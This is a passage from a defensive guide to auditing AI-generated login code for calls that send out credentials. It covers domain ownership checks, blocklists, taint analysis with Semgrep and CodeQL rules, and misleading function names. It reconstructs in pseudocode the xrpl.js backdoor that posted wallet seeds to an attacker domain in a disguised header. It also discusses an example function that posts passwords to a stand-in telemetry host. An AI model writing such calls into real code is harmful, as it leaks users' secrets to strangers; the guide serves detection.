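The easiest way to identify a host's owner is to read its name from the right. The host id.shop.example.login.example belongs to whoever owns login.example, not to the bookshop. An @ sign can also mislead. A request to `https://id.shop.example@login.example/` goes to login.example, and the part before the sign is only a username. A URL parser, the library function that splits an address into its parts, handles both cases correctly, but it won't detect a lookalike such as 1ogin.example, which starts with the digit one.

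For a well-known service, the reviewer can compare the address character by character with the one in the service's official documentation. The reviewer has to find that documentation independently, because the scammers behind SolanaAPIs had documentation too.

Asking a language model for the right address is risky. Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams* reports that researchers asked a model where to log in to 50 brands. The model gave 131 host names, and the brands did not control 34% of them. ThaiCERT's *Experts Warn of New Phishing Threats Using LLMs as Scammers Exploit AI* (2025) identifies the model as GPT-4.1, which newer models have since replaced. The test also asked for login pages rather than the addresses that programs use, so the 34% is a poor guide to how often a current coding assistant would give a wrong address.

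Nearly 30% of the domains, including most of the wrong answers, were unregistered, parked (registered but unused) or otherwise inactive. A request to an unregistered domain is harmless for now, but anyone can register the domain, and the login code will then send passwords to the new owner without any change to the program.

*Investigating Security Implications of Automatically Generated Code on the Software Supply Chain* (2025) describes SSCGuard, a tool that looks for this problem in generated code. SSCGuard sends a request to each address in the code and, if it can't reach the server, checks with the domain seller GoDaddy whether the domain is available. A reviewer can do the same by hand for the few hosts in a login service, and should remove any request to an available domain.

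Registration records usually show when someone registered a domain. A registration date shortly before the request appeared in the code is a reason to look more closely, although new companies also need new domains. A date after the request appeared is more worrying. The model may have made up the address and someone then bought the domain, or an older registration may have lapsed and the domain changed hands. An old domain isn't necessarily safe, because scam sites can stay online for years.

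Some programs use a numeric IP address instead of a domain name. Microsoft lists four such addresses among the servers that controlled infected computers in the campaign it reported. A numeric address has no domain registration to look up, and public records often name only the hosting company that owns the block of numbers. Legitimate programs use numeric addresses for machines on a private network, in ranges such as 10.0.0.0 to 10.255.255.255, which the public internet doesn't route. A public numeric address in login code is harder to justify, since a supplier that expects customers to trust it with passwords can afford a domain.

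### Addresses that only exist at run time

The full address of a request is often missing from the source for innocent reasons. Most of the YoMix programs build it by joining a fixed base, which includes the host, to a path such as /mix. The reviewer can still read the host from the base. The risk is greater when the program builds the host itself, as in this line:

```python
url = "https://" + region + ".shop.example/login"
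```

Suppose the code builds a URL by putting the variable `region` before ".shop.example". If `region` is "eu", the request goes to eu.shop.example. But if someone can set `region` to "login.example/", the request goes to login.example, and the rest of the URL becomes part of the path. The reviewer therefore has to trace where `region` comes from and which values it can take.

A program can also download the address it sends data to. In the campaign Microsoft described, the first server that an infected computer contacted supplied the address of a second server, which then sent it commands. The original project did not contain the second address. Legitimate login code can do something similar when it uses OpenID Connect, a common standard for signing in through another company. The program can download a document from the identity provider that lists the addresses to use. A redirect can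 also send data to an address that isn't in the code. Status code 307 means that the program should send the same request, including its body, to another address, and Python's requests library does so by default.

In these cases, reading the source code isn't enough to complete step 2. The inventory should name the host that supplies the address, and the program should compare the supplied host with the allowed destinations before sending it a credential. Network rules can enforce the same list from outside the program.

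### What reputation services miss

A reputation service is a database that classifies web addresses as malicious or safe. Checking every host in the code against one takes seconds, and Chen and colleagues argue that coding assistants should do this automatically before they return any code. To their knowledge, no production model did so when they wrote. A warning is a good reason to stop and investigate, but the absence of one is much weaker evidence that a host is safe.

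The services give different verdicts even on known scams. One model put the address yomix[.]io/api/v1 in its code. In slides for a conference talk, Chen and colleagues show that ChainPatrol and SecLookup classify it as malicious, while Google Safe Browsing classifies it as safe. Their paper gives Google's result for the same address as "Unknown threat on Unknown platform", which a hurried reader could mistake for a warning. Anyone who automates these checks needs to know how each service reports that it has no record.

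Agreement between blocklists can also mislead. When GPT-4o put a different YoMix address in its code, ChainPatrol blocked the address based only on MetaMask's blocklist. A reviewer who checked both would have counted the same entry twice.

New scam sites also take time to reach the lists. Chen and colleagues think the 62 sites that MetaMask listed after their report had probably been online for more than a year, because the models' training data ended in August 2024 or earlier. But some of the sites could be newer if a model guessed their addresses rather than learning them from its training data.

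When benchmark requests named no scam site, the models answered with addresses at 1,853 malicious domains. About 60% of those domains (1,105) were on neither of the two blocklists Chen and colleagues started from. The 1,853 total excludes any scam that all three detectors missed.

Scam databases typically list only live sites, so an address can be missing because its site is down, even if the owner could bring it back. Many of the newly found addresses no longer worked when Chen and colleagues rechecked them. Lists can also wrongly flag a site, for instance when its legitimate owner has recovered it from a hijacker but the warning remains. And a list can go out of use, as PhishFort's did during the study.

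Services that scan files have a similar delay. Goldberg, in *New Malicious VS Code Extension Backdoor*, describes an editor extension from May 2026 that downloaded and ran an attacker's commands every time the editor started. When Knostic checked the extension on VirusTotal, a website that runs files through many scanners, none had flagged it. Knostic sells a competing way of catching such extensions, but it is unsurprising that scanners would miss a brand-new file. A host that a thief set up last week may also go unflagged, so the reviewer still has to find out who controls it.

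### Strangers on well-known hosts

Attackers can run malicious services at addresses under a legitimate company's domain. Vercel, for example, is a hosting company that gives customers' projects names ending in vercel.app. Microsoft lists 13 vercel.app hosts that the attackers used to deliver malicious code or receive stolen settings. One of them, api-web3-auth[.]vercel[.]app, could pass for part of a login system.

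The age and reputation of vercel.app don't show whether a project created there yesterday is safe. Allowing all of vercel.app would have allowed all 13 hosts. Legitimate projects use it too, so blocking all of it would stop them, and one of Microsoft's suggested searches, for server programs that contact vercel.app, can only produce leads to follow up. The same problem arises with pages.dev, where Cloudflare hosts its customers' websites. Five of the eight entries in the scam blocklist sample that Chen and colleagues show in their slides end in pages.dev.

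On GitHub, the host name is the same for everyone and the owner's name comes after it, as in github.com/owner/project. *Beware of Agentic Botnets* (2026) reports that when models were asked for the addresses of recently popular projects, they named the wrong owner for 92% of the projects tested. Anyone could register some of the wrong names, and coding assistants downloaded projects from the wrong addresses. An owner can also change after a reviewer has approved the address. According to *Investigating Security Implications of Automatically Generated Code on the Software Supply Chain*, GitHub redirects visitors when an account changes its name, but a stranger may be able to register the old name, which breaks the redirect.

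The inventory should therefore record enough of each address to identify its owner. For an ordinary company, the domain is enough. For a Vercel project, the inventory should record the full host name, and for GitHub, it should also include the account name in the path. The path is also needed for webhook.site, where the malicious package gmgeoip sent the file it stole, because anyone can create an address there to receive data and only the path distinguishes one user's address from another's.

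### Telemetry and exfiltration

Many legitimate programs send their makers data that users never think about, so a reviewer needs a way to tell acceptable telemetry from exfiltration. Zargarov, a researcher at Akamai, analysed a borderline case called CodeAudit AI, a Visual Studio Code extension that offers code review by a language model. A user who asks for a review expects the extension to upload the code being reviewed.

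CodeAudit AI also monitored every edit. Whenever the user pasted more than about 50 characters, it uploaded the pasted text with the file name, the project's path and a user identifier. The review commands checked for consent before sending anything, but this automatic upload did not. At start-up and at other times, the extension also sent project details, such as the folder structure and the address of the code repository. It sent all of this to a hardcoded address over plain HTTP, so anyone able to monitor the network could read it, including any password or API key in the pasted text.

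Zargarov accepts that some of these functions may support legitimate features, such as comparing pasted code with other code. The analysis contains no evidence that anyone misused the data, and it ends by recommending an Akamai product. But the maker had published no description of what the extension collects, and reviewing one piece of code on request doesn't require everything else the user pastes. The maker had no right to that text even if its intentions were good, so the upload was an exfiltration call.

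GitHub's code-analysis extension for the same editor also sends data to GitHub. GitHub's *Telemetry in CodeQL for Visual Studio Code* explains that the extension collects usage data only if the user has left the editor's telemetry setting on. GitHub says it uses the data to improve the extension, does not share it outside the company, and stores IP addresses and installation identifiers for at most 30 days and anonymous data for at most 180. A CodeQL request and a CodeAudit AI request could look the same in the source. The differences are that GitHub tells users what it collects and can reasonably need usage data to improve a product.

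Making code readable does not replace telling users where it sends their data. Knostic examined twelve extensions, most of them presented as tools for running code or similar jobs, whose code would send a user's chat messages and pasted code to outside servers. Ten hid this function until the program ran, and two contained it as ordinary readable JavaScript. Knostic read the code but did not observe it sending anything. A user who installed one of the two readable extensions just to run code would have been no better informed than a user of the other ten.

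Disclosure isn't enough on its own either. Suppose the owner of the earlier login function says that telemetry.example.net belongs to an analytics company and mentions it in the site's privacy policy. The function would still send that company every user's password, which isn't needed to count logins.

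## Tracing the password to the request

The data each request sends is often the hardest part of a request inventory to fill in, because a password may pass through several variables and helper functions, with a new name each time, before it leaves the program. Taint analysis automates the search by marking sensitive data where it enters the program and tracking it everywhere the program uses it. Some tools do this while the program runs, but most code scanners work from the source alone.

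Security teams usually use taint analysis to mark untrusted input and look for paths from it to functions where it could do damage, such as one that runs database commands. To find an exfiltration call, they use the same algorithm but mark the program's own secrets and look for paths out to the network.

### How the mark spreads

The team first chooses the sources and sinks. In login code, the sources are the password field, session tokens, API keys and any private key the program reads from a file. The sinks are the arguments of every function that can send data out, including the address and headers as well as the body.

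The tool then builds a data-flow graph, which GitHub's *About data flow analysis*, part of the documentation for its code-searching tool CodeQL, contrasts with the syntax tree. The graph's nodes are the parts of the program that hold a value when it runs, and an edge between two nodes means that data can move from the first to the second. Plain data-flow analysis follows only unchanged values. Taint analysis adds edges for values computed from other values, so after `y = x + 1` a mark on `x` spreads to `y`. A mark on a password likewise spreads to the result when the program joins the password to other text or encodes it in base64.

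With the graph in place, the rest is a search:

1. Put every source in a set T of marked nodes.
2. For each edge from a node in T to a node outside it, add the second node to T, unless the team has declared that node safe.
3. Repeat step 2 until T stops growing.
4. Report every sink in T.

The search always ends because the graph has a finite number of nodes and T never shrinks. Its accuracy depends on whether the edges are right. Semgrep, a scanner whose rules resemble the code they match, provides some edges automatically. According to Semgrep's *Taint analysis*, marks spread by default through assignments and operators, and from a function call's inputs to its output.

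Semgrep can lose track of a marked value when a program stores it in a container. In an example from Semgrep's *Advanced taint analysis techniques*, a program adds a marked value to a set with `s.add(x)` and later takes an item out. Semgrep misses this flow until the rule's author writes a propagator, a line specifying that `add` carries the mark from `x` to `s`. Semgrep then marks the whole set, including any harmless item that the program takes out of it.

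### The login function, line by line

The earlier login function posts the password to id.example.com and then to telemetry.example.net. The search of this function starts with the `password` parameter as its only source.

| Code | Effect |
|---|---|
| `def log_in(username, password):` | `password` gets the mark |
| `{"username": username, "password": password}` | The dictionary gets the mark because it contains the password |
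| `reply = requests.post("https://id.example.com/v1/verify", json=...)` | First report: marked data reaches a network sink |
| The same dictionary, built again | The second dictionary gets the mark |
| `requests.post("https://telemetry.example.net/v1/events", json=...)` | Second report: marked data reaches a network sink |
| `if reply.status_code != 200:` | No report, because this line sends nothing |
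| `return reply.json()["session_token"]` | A new secret appears, which the team can make a source of its own |

The variable `reply` holds the identity provider's response, which doesn't contain the password, but Semgrep can't determine that from a call into the requests library. When Semgrep has no definition for a function, it marks the function's output if any input was marked. Unless the rule overrides this default, Semgrep will treat both `reply` and the session token inside it as passwords, and a later request that sends the token somewhere will produce a misleading report.

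The `taint_assume_safe_functions` setting turns the default off, but then a call that encodes the password would also remove the mark unless the team wrote a propagator for it. For finding exfiltration calls, it seems better to keep the default and make an exception for the response.

The rule "a password must not reach the network" has now produced two reports. The first is a false positive, because the identity provider must receive the password to check it. Even if someone deleted the exfiltration call, the rule would still flag this legitimate request at every scan. Most teams would soon suppress the rule, perhaps for the whole login service.

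### Adding the allowed destinations

The rule needs to know where each kind of data may go. Let s be a kind of data, d a destination, and A(s) the set of destinations allowed for s. The tool should report a flow from s to d only when

d ∉ A(s)

which means that d is not in A(s). The bookshop's inventory contained the same permissions, but it grouped them by host. In readable pseudocode, the rule for the login function is:

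```
allowed[PASSWORD]      = { id.example.com }
allowed[SESSION_TOKEN] = { }

for each request r in the program:
    H = the hosts that r might contact
    for each kind of data s that reaches r:
        if H may be incomplete:
            report "s may go to an unknown host"
        for each host d in H:
            if d is not in allowed[s]:
                report "s goes to d"
```

In the first request, s is PASSWORD and d is id.example.com. That host is in `allowed[PASSWORD]`, so the tool reports nothing. In the second, s is again PASSWORD but d is telemetry.example.net, which is not in the set. The tool's only report is now "PASSWORD goes to telemetry.example.net".

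The set for session tokens is empty because the website returns the token to the browser in its login response, and no outgoing request needs it. If the team later adds a service that needs the token, someone will have to edit the set, which is a good time to ask who runs the service.

The comparison should use the complete host name and, on shared hosts such as webhook.site, the path as well. A rule that only checks whether the address contains "id.example.com" would accept any longer host name that includes it.

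### Sending part of a secret on purpose

A breached-password lookup breaks the rule as it stands. The five hash digits that the website sends carry the password's mark because they come from the password, and the lookup service isn't in `allowed[PASSWORD]`. The service shouldn't be added, because the website would then be allowed to send it the whole password.

In *Understanding Have I Been Pwned's Use of SHA-1 and k-Anonymity*, Hunt describes looking up the password P@ssw0rd on his own service. The password's SHA-1 hash has 40 hexadecimal digits (0 to 9 and A to F) and begins 21BD12DC. The website sent only the first five digits, 21BD1. The service returned 788 lines, each containing the other 35 digits of a hash that starts with 21BD1 and the number of times the corresponding password had appeared in stolen data. The website searched these lines for the rest of the password's hash and found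 it, with a count of 83,129. Nothing it sent to the service showed which line had matched.

Have I Been Pwned's *API Documentation* gives the number of possible prefixes:

16⁵ = 1,048,576

A typical search now returns about 800 hashes. Hunt chose five digits as a compromise. Using four would make each response 16 times as long, while using six would make it a sixteenth as long and leave fewer candidates for the real password. The service's email search uses six because the service covers far more email addresses than passwords.

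Five hexadecimal digits make up 20 of the hash's 160 bits. They can help a thief guess the password, because a thief usually has a list of likely ones. If the thief hashed a billion candidates and kept those that matched the prefix, about 950 would be left. Some of those would be likelier than others. Hunt prints five of the 788 lines for the prefix 21BD1. One is for P@ssw0rd, and the other four passwords had each turned up three times at most, so anyone who saw the prefix would try P@ssw0rd first. Hunt writes that the six-digit email prefix reveals nothing useful about the address, but that would be too strong a claim for passwords.

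The lookup is still reasonable, mainly because the request doesn't contain a username. When the website's own server sends it, the service has nothing to link those 950 guesses to a particular account. Adding the username to the same five digits would make the request much more dangerous.

Sending the complete hash could expose the password. Hunt points out that a web search is enough to recover a common password from its complete hash. Cloudflare's *Validating Leaked Passwords with k-Anonymity* describes the partial search as a way to avoid disclosing a complete unsalted hash, meaning one computed without adding random data to the password.

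Have I Been Pwned warns against running a lookup after every character the user types, because someone who can see these repeated requests may also be able to work out the password. The first prefix comes from a single character, so the observer can hash all 95 possibilities on a standard US keyboard and see which one matches. Once that character is known, the second also has only 95 possibilities. A 12-character password would take at most 12 × 95 = 1,140 hashes, even though each request would still send only five digits of the hash to the right host. The website should therefore run the lookup once, after the user has finished typing.

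The length of the response can reveal something about the prefix to a person watching the encrypted traffic, since different prefixes return different numbers of hashes. To prevent this, a website can ask the service to pad the response with dummy entries to a random length of 800 to 1,000 records.

Computer scientists call a deliberate release of information derived from a secret declassification. In code, the safest place for it is a short function that does nothing else:

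```python
import hashlib

def breach_prefix(password):
    digest = hashlib.sha1(password.encode("utf-8")).hexdigest()
    return digest[:5]
```

The team tells the tool that this function takes a PASSWORD and returns a PASSWORD_PREFIX, and adds one line to the list:

```
allowed[PASSWORD_PREFIX] = { api.pwnedpasswords.com }
```

The tool now accepts the lookup but still reports requests that send the password or its complete hash to the same service, or the prefix to any other host. Declaring the function's output safe would be easier, but the tool would then miss requests that send the prefix elsewhere, together with the username.

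The tool relies on the team's description of what `breach_prefix` returns and doesn't check it. If someone changed the last line to return the whole digest, every scan would still pass. A test that the result is exactly five characters long would catch that change, and the team should require an experienced reviewer's approval for any other edit to the function.

### Where the tracking fails

A clean result means the tool found no forbidden flow in its graph of the program, but the graph may be missing some of the program's flows.

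The trace often breaks where the password is stored. Suppose the login function writes a password to a log file, and an hour later another program uploads the file to a hosted log service. A tool that examines the two programs separately won't connect the password to the upload. To catch this, the team can treat files, databases and message queues as destinations too. None of them should be an allowed destination for a plain-text password.

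These tools can also miss leaks through outside libraries. CodeQL doesn't inspect the source code of a program's dependencies, as the software consultancy Tweag (2025) explains in an introduction to the tool. Someone has to describe what each library function does. In Tweag's example, the user has to declare `sarge.run`, which runs an operating-system command, as a sink. Semgrep is cautious by default and keeps the mark on whatever an unknown function returns, but it doesn't report a library call that sends the password over the network and returns nothing unless someone has listed that call as a sink.

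Two variables can also refer to the same object in memory. If that object is a dictionary, a password added through one variable can be read through the other. Semgrep tracks marks by variable and doesn't follow such aliases. GitHub lists aliasing as one difficulty in computing an accurate data-flow graph.

Other destinations can't be read from the source because they come from a setting, a downloaded document or a redirect. The pseudocode reports these as unknown instead of letting them pass. Some are easy to resolve. Semgrep lists constant propagation as a feature of its paid analysis, which can work out a fixed address defined in another file. An address that depends on the live server's configuration has to be checked at run time.

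The last gap is harder to close because information can travel without any value being copied. When a login function writes "login failed" to its audit log, anyone who reads the log learns that the password was wrong, although the message contains no part of it. The password only decided which branch of an `if` statement ran. According to GitHub's documentation, an `if` statement has no node in the data-flow graph because it controls the order of execution and carries no value. A mark on the password therefore never reaches the message.

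One such message reveals very little, but a program could in principle disclose a whole secret through the branches it takes, and a tool that follows only values would report nothing. Marking everything that depends on a branch would be a poor fix for login code, because nearly everything after the password check depends on its result, including the session token and the page the user sees. The tool would flag almost every request that followed.

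Semgrep's paid version has an option for tracking control flow, which only checks whether execution can get from one place in the code to another. A team could use it to list every network call that can run after the program reads a password, but the list would include legitimate calls too.

Published counts give a rough idea of how much these gaps matter. Ryan, Ifti and colleagues (2025), in *Unveiling Malicious Logic*, labelled the hostile statements in 370 malicious packages from PyPI. The packages averaged 1.05 malicious files each, and each piece of hostile behaviour took up about two lines. Code that compact leaves little room for data to pass through many files. But 86% of the labelled behaviour was in setup.py, which runs when someone installs a package, and an attacker who adds code to a login function may work differently.

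The same data is useful for choosing sinks. Of the 174 instances of exfiltration that Ryan and colleagues labelled, three used DNS tunnelling, which hides data in the lookups that turn host names into numeric addresses. A sink list of only HTTP functions would miss those three.

### What CodeQL and Semgrep leave to the team

CodeQL's built-in Python queries don't appear to include one that looks for passwords going to the wrong host. GitHub's list had 48 queries in August 2026, and none of their names refers to a secret in an outgoing request. Two look for sensitive information in clear text, one in logs and one in storage, which helps with the storage gap.

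Three of the 48 queries concern outgoing requests. One looks for requests that skip the certificate check. The other two look for request forgery, in which an outsider gets the program to contact an address the outsider chooses. GitHub's *Full server-side request forgery* describes the fault as putting user input into a request without validating it, and the query focuses on how much of the address an attacker can control. In the login function, both addresses are fixed text and both requests use the normal certificate check, so all three queries should miss the exfiltration call.

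GitHub's *File data in outbound network request* documents a closer match for JavaScript, a query that flags code that reads a local file and sends the contents to a remote address. Its example comes from a backdoor in two packages on npm, the main public repository for JavaScript. The backdoor read a settings file that may hold secret npm tokens and put the contents in the Referer header, which normally names the page a visitor came from.

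That query would have caught the npm backdoor, but it tracks data read from files, and a password in a login function usually arrives over the network. It also has no list of allowed hosts. GitHub rates its precision as medium and advises users to examine the highlighted code closely, so the reviewer must decide who may receive the data. The query is in CodeQL's extended sets, not the default one.

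Either tool can apply the allowed-destinations rule once the team supplies the missing parts:

| What the team supplies | In CodeQL | In Semgrep |
|---|---|---|
| Secrets to track | `isSource` | `pattern-sources` |
| Calls that send data | `isSink` | `pattern-sinks` |
| Flows the tool can't see | `isAdditionalFlowStep` | `pattern-propagators` |
| Places where the mark stops | `isBarrier` | `pattern-sanitizers` |
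| Allowed hosts | A condition in the query | An exception in the sink pattern |

GitHub's *Analyzing data flow in Python* describes a predefined CodeQL source, `RemoteFlowSource`, for everything that reaches a program over the network. In a web application, that includes the password, the username, the search terms and the preferred language. A query that used `RemoteFlowSource` unchanged would report far too much, so the team should narrow it to the fields that hold secrets. CodeQL automatically keeps the mark on data that passes through encoding functions it recognises.

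CodeQL also has a class for outgoing HTTP requests that can return the parts of the code that contribute to the address. GitHub notes that one request may have several such parts. The query's author has to combine them before comparing the host with the list. For a library function that CodeQL doesn't cover, the team can add a sink in a separate data file. Each entry identifies the function's argument and the kind of query that should treat it as a sink, as in GitHub's example for a package that runs commands.

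In outline, a Semgrep rule for the login function looks like this:

```yaml
rules:
  - id: password-to-unlisted-address
    mode: taint
    languages: [python]
    severity: ERROR
    message: This request sends a password to an unlisted address.
    pattern-sources:
      - patterns:
          - pattern-inside: |
              def log_in($USER, $PASSWORD):
                  ...
          - focus-metavariable: $PASSWORD
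    pattern-sinks:
      - patterns:
          - pattern: requests.post($URL, ..., json=$DATA, ...)
          - pattern-not: requests.post("https://id.example.com/v1/verify", ...)
          - focus-metavariable: $DATA
```

The source is the second parameter of `log_in`. The sink is the `json` argument of any call to `requests.post`, except calls to the identity provider's exact address, the only destination the `pattern-not` line allows. A rule used in production would also need to cover headers, other ways of passing the body, other request functions and every other place where a password enters the program.

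The team can use Semgrep's taint labels to track several kinds of data in one rule. A source can attach a label such as PASSWORD or CAPTCHA_KEY, and a sink can require a particular label. The rule could then allow the site's key to go to the CAPTCHA supplier's address but still report a password sent there.

The free edition of Semgrep could run the example, because the source and both requests are in the same function. According to Semgrep, that edition analyses only one function at a time. It would stop tracking the password if `log_in` passed it to a helper that made the request, as several of the YoMix programs do. The paid product follows data between functions by default, and between files if the customer turns that on.

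Semgrep doesn't run cross-file analysis when it scans a pull request. A full scan also falls back to analyzing one file at a time if the cross-file preparation needs more than 5 GB of memory or the scan takes longer than three hours. An exfiltration call in a helper file could therefore get through the pull request scan and turn up only in the next full scan. A team that depends on cross-file tracking should run a full scan before each release and confirm that it didn't fall back.

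## Misleading names and obfuscated logic

An attacker can disguise an exfiltration call in two ways. Obfuscation makes code hard to read, for example by storing an encoded address and decoding it only at runtime. Mislabelling leaves the code readable but gives it a name or comment that describes something harmless. A search can find many kinds of obfuscation, but mislabelled code looks ordinary until someone compares the label with what the code does.

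### The xrpl.js compromise

In April 2025, an attacker used a mislabelled function to collect cryptocurrency keys through xrpl.js, the official JavaScript library for the XRP Ledger, a blockchain. The Hacker News (2025) reported that the library had more than 135,000 weekly downloads. The attacker phished an employee of Ripple, the company that launched the ledger, and used the employee's npm account to publish five malicious versions of the library.

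This was a hijacked package, not generated code. It is still a good model for generated login code, because the disguise consisted of a few well-chosen names, and a language model chooses such names whenever it writes a function. Eriksen, in *XRP supply chain attack*, a post for the security company Aikido, shows the function that sent the keys. In pseudocode, it works like this:

```
to run checkValidityOfSeed on a seed:
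    stop if validSeeds already contains the seed
    put the seed into validSeeds
    send a POST request to 0x9c[.]xyz/xc, with the seed in the header "ad-referral"
```

A wallet's seed is the secret from which the library computes the private key, so anyone who has the seed controls the wallet. The function `checkValidityOfSeed` sends the seed to a stranger's server, although its name suggests that it tests whether a seed is well formed. The set named `validSeeds` can contain any text, and its only effect is to stop the function from sending the same secret twice.

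The seed is sent in a header named `ad-referral`, which sounds like advertising data. The request has no body, so a reviewer who read only request bodies would have missed the seed.

The attacker added calls to this function in seven places, including the constructor, which runs whenever a program creates a wallet object. Generating a new wallet runs the function four times, twice with the seed and twice with the private key, but because of the set, it sends only two requests, one for each secret.

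The same file contains a real check, `validateMnemonic`, which the library calls before it restores a wallet from a list of words. If the words are invalid, the library stops with an error. A few lines further down, `checkValidityOfSeed` returns nothing and raises no error of its own, so the program continues the same way whether or not the seed is valid. The program also passes private keys and lists of words to this function. These have different formats from a seed, so no ordinary seed test could work for all three.

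### Five versions in an hour

*Malicious Supply Chain Compromise in xrpl.js npm Package* (2025), the official disclosure, dates the phishing to 20:39 UTC on 21 April. The first malicious version appeared seven minutes later and the last about an hour after that.

| Version | Published (UTC) | Malicious content |
|---|---|---|
| 4.2.1 | 20:46 | Two built files, which a tool normally generates from the source |
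| 4.2.2 | 20:55 | The built files and the compiled wallet code |
| 4.2.3 | 21:32 | The TypeScript source too |
| 2.14.2 | 21:37 | A release in the library's older 2.x series |
| 4.2.4 | 21:49 | The TypeScript source too |

At first the attacker pasted code into the built files by hand. Later versions had the function in the source code, and the compiler included it in the built files. Eriksen concludes that the attacker was trying different ways to keep the backdoor hidden.

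Aikido noticed the attack through a monitoring service that uses language models to read new packages on npm and similar sites. At 20:53, the service flagged odd code in the package. Eriksen then found that the domain was brand new and searched for calls to the function. The new packages had no matching releases on GitHub, where the latest version was 4.2.0. According to the disclosure, the attacker published straight to npm and never altered the GitHub repository, so anyone reviewing the code there would have seen only the legitimate version.

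Aikido sells access to this service, and one success doesn't show how often it raises false alarms. Ripple heard about the attack at 8:14 the next morning, more than eleven hours after the alert, and had published clean versions by 12:34. Ripple knew of no resulting thefts when it wrote the disclosure, but it told everyone who had installed a malicious version to assume their wallets were compromised.

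### Why readers believe a name

*Linguistic antipatterns* (Arnaoudova, Di Penta and Antoniol, 2015) draws on Brooks's 1983 theory of how programmers understand code. In this theory, a reader starts with a vague guess about what a program does and refines it using names and comments, only sometimes inspecting the code in detail. A wrong guess is hard to give up.

A misleading name can do more harm than a meaningless one. *Considerations and Pitfalls in Controlled Experiments on Code Comprehension* (2021) describes an experiment by Avidan and Feitelson in which misleading names hindered readers more than consecutive letters of the alphabet did. If the xrpl.js attacker had named the function `a`, a reviewer would have had to read its three lines to learn what it was for.

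Several consistent labels are no better evidence than one if the same person wrote them all. In July 2026, an attacker added a key stealer to a library for the Injective blockchain with about 175,000 monthly downloads. *Not-so-anonymous telemetry* (Obregoso, Tafani-Dereeper and Salem, 2026) shows that the title of the code change, the comment at the top and the function name `trackKeyDerivation` all described usage statistics. OSV's *MAL-2026-10165* (2026), an entry in a public vulnerability database, gives the file name as `key-derivation-telemetry.ts`.

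According to the comment, the function recorded which of two methods people used to load a wallet, and when. That required only the method's name and the time, but the library called `trackKeyDerivation('fm', words)`, where `words` is the list of words that controls the wallet. A reviewer could have caught the theft from that line alone by asking why a usage count needed the second argument.

The function encoded the secret and sent it in a header named X-Request-Id, which normally holds a reference number for the request. Socket (2024) reports a similar attack on a Solana library in December 2024, in which a function named `addToQueue` sent private keys in headers that looked like Cloudflare's. All three attacks sent the secret in a header, so a reviewer should read a request's headers as closely as its body.

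### Five questions about a network call

Based on these cases, reviewers can ask five questions about any network call in login code. The answer to each question can be the same for legitimate and malicious code.

| Question | xrpl.js | Injective | Honest code with the same answer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Does the function do what its name suggests? | No, it validates nothing | Only in part, because it also sends the secret | Old functions that have outgrown their names |
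| Does the program use the response? | No | No | Audit logs |
| Does the code hide errors? | No | Yes | Telemetry that must not interrupt a login |
| Does the call run on every login (here, every time a wallet loads)? | Yes, but it sends each secret once | Yes, for the two main ways of loading a key | The password check itself |
| Did someone ask for it? | No | No | Logging that a careful programmer adds unasked |

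A reviewer can spot a misleading function name by covering it, describing the body in a few words, and comparing the two. `checkValidityOfSeed`, for example, would be more accurately named `sendSecretOnce`. *Deep Learning-Based Identification of Inconsistent Method Names* (2025) describes research tools that work in much the same way, generating a name from a function's body and checking the existing name against it.

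Simpler tools can check part of this by rule. Arnaoudova and colleagues list 17 common mismatches, including functions whose names begin with a word such as "check" or "validate" but which don't report the result to the caller. *IDEAL* (Peruma, Arnaoudova and Newman, 2021) detects this mismatch in Java and C# by flagging functions whose names start with a validation word but which return no value and throw no exception. `checkValidityOfSeed` fits this rule exactly, although IDEAL doesn't cover TypeScript.

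The rule matched 446 functions in four popular open-source projects. Peruma and colleagues read 166 of them and found the mismatch in 165. The rule is therefore very good at finding badly named functions, but there is no reason to think those projects contained code that steals data. Programmers also tend to leave such names alone. Arnaoudova and colleagues pointed out 47 mismatches of various kinds to the developers responsible, who removed five. A match is a reason to read the function, and the reviewer can start with functions that also make a network call.

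An attacker hides errors so that a failure of the server receiving the stolen data doesn't attract attention. The Injective code discarded any error from its request. The xrpl.js code did not, and in current versions of Node.js, which runs JavaScript on servers, an unhandled failure of this kind stops the whole program by default. The earlier Python login function has the same weakness. If telemetry.example.net were down, `requests.post` would raise an error and nobody could log in.

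How often a call runs helps distinguish exfiltration from ordinary set-up. A program may contact an identity provider once at startup to download its settings, but a request that collects passwords has to run when people log in. A request that runs before the password check finishes deserves especially close review, because most legitimate logging needs the result.

If a team keeps the instructions it gave the model, it can check whether the generated code makes requests that nobody asked for. Suppose a programmer asked for a function that checks a password with id.example.com. The function needs only one request to do that, so a second request to telemetry.example.net is extra. Models often add things nobody asked for, such as logging, so an extra request isn't proof of an attack. The team should still delete it unless someone can say why they want it.

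The programmer's instructions are a separate record of what the generated code should contain, roughly as the GitHub releases were for xrpl.js. They don't help if the programmer asked for a service by name and the model supplied a scammer's address for it, as in the wallet theft of 2024. In that case the task required the network call, so only a check of its destination would find the problem.

### Signs of obfuscation

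Obfuscated code usually includes steps that convert hidden text back into a form the computer can use. A reviewer can look for these steps, but they all have legitimate uses too.

| Sign | Honest use | When to worry |
|---|---|---|
| Encoded text that the program decodes as it runs | Images, certificates, HTTP's basic login header | The result is an address or program code |
| An address built from pieces | A host from the settings joined to a path | Every piece is already fixed in the source |
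| A function that the program looks up by name as it runs | Plug-ins, such as a choice of sign-in methods | The program decodes or assembles the name first |
| Downloaded code that the program runs | Installers, updaters, scripts on a web page | It happens inside a login server |
| Encrypted text | Protected settings, with the key kept elsewhere | The key is in the same file |
| Code without spaces or meaningful names | Smaller downloads for browsers | Nobody can produce the same file from the source |

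The Injective attacker's address was stored as a list of 49 numbers, one for each character, which the program converted to text and joined. A legitimate program builds an address from pieces because one of them may change, for example when the program moves from a test server to the live one. None of the 49 numbers could change, so the list served only to hide the address.

The same reasoning applies to a key stored next to the text it decrypts. Ryan and colleagues show a malicious package with the key and the encrypted text in a single statement. Anyone who has the file can decrypt the text, so the encryption only stops people from reading it at a glance.

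Encoded addresses are often easy to find. An address that begins with "http" always begins with "aHR0c" in standard base64, so a reviewer can search source and configuration files for those five characters. Attackers can encode text in other ways, so a search that finds nothing doesn't prove the file is safe. The reviewer should decode any encoded string in a separate tool, never by running the program.

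Minified browser files need a different check because they are hard to read even when they contain nothing malicious. The first malicious version of xrpl.js changed only files of this kind, apart from some settings. A team can rebuild such a file from source code it has reviewed and compare the result with the file it received.

PyPI's *Acceptable Use Policy* prohibits content that "uses obfuscation techniques to hide or mask functionality", whether or not the hidden function is harmful. The same rule seems sensible for generated login code. A programmer who asks for a login function has no reason to want the address encoded and can ask the model for a plain version or write the line by hand.

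### What 370 malicious packages contained

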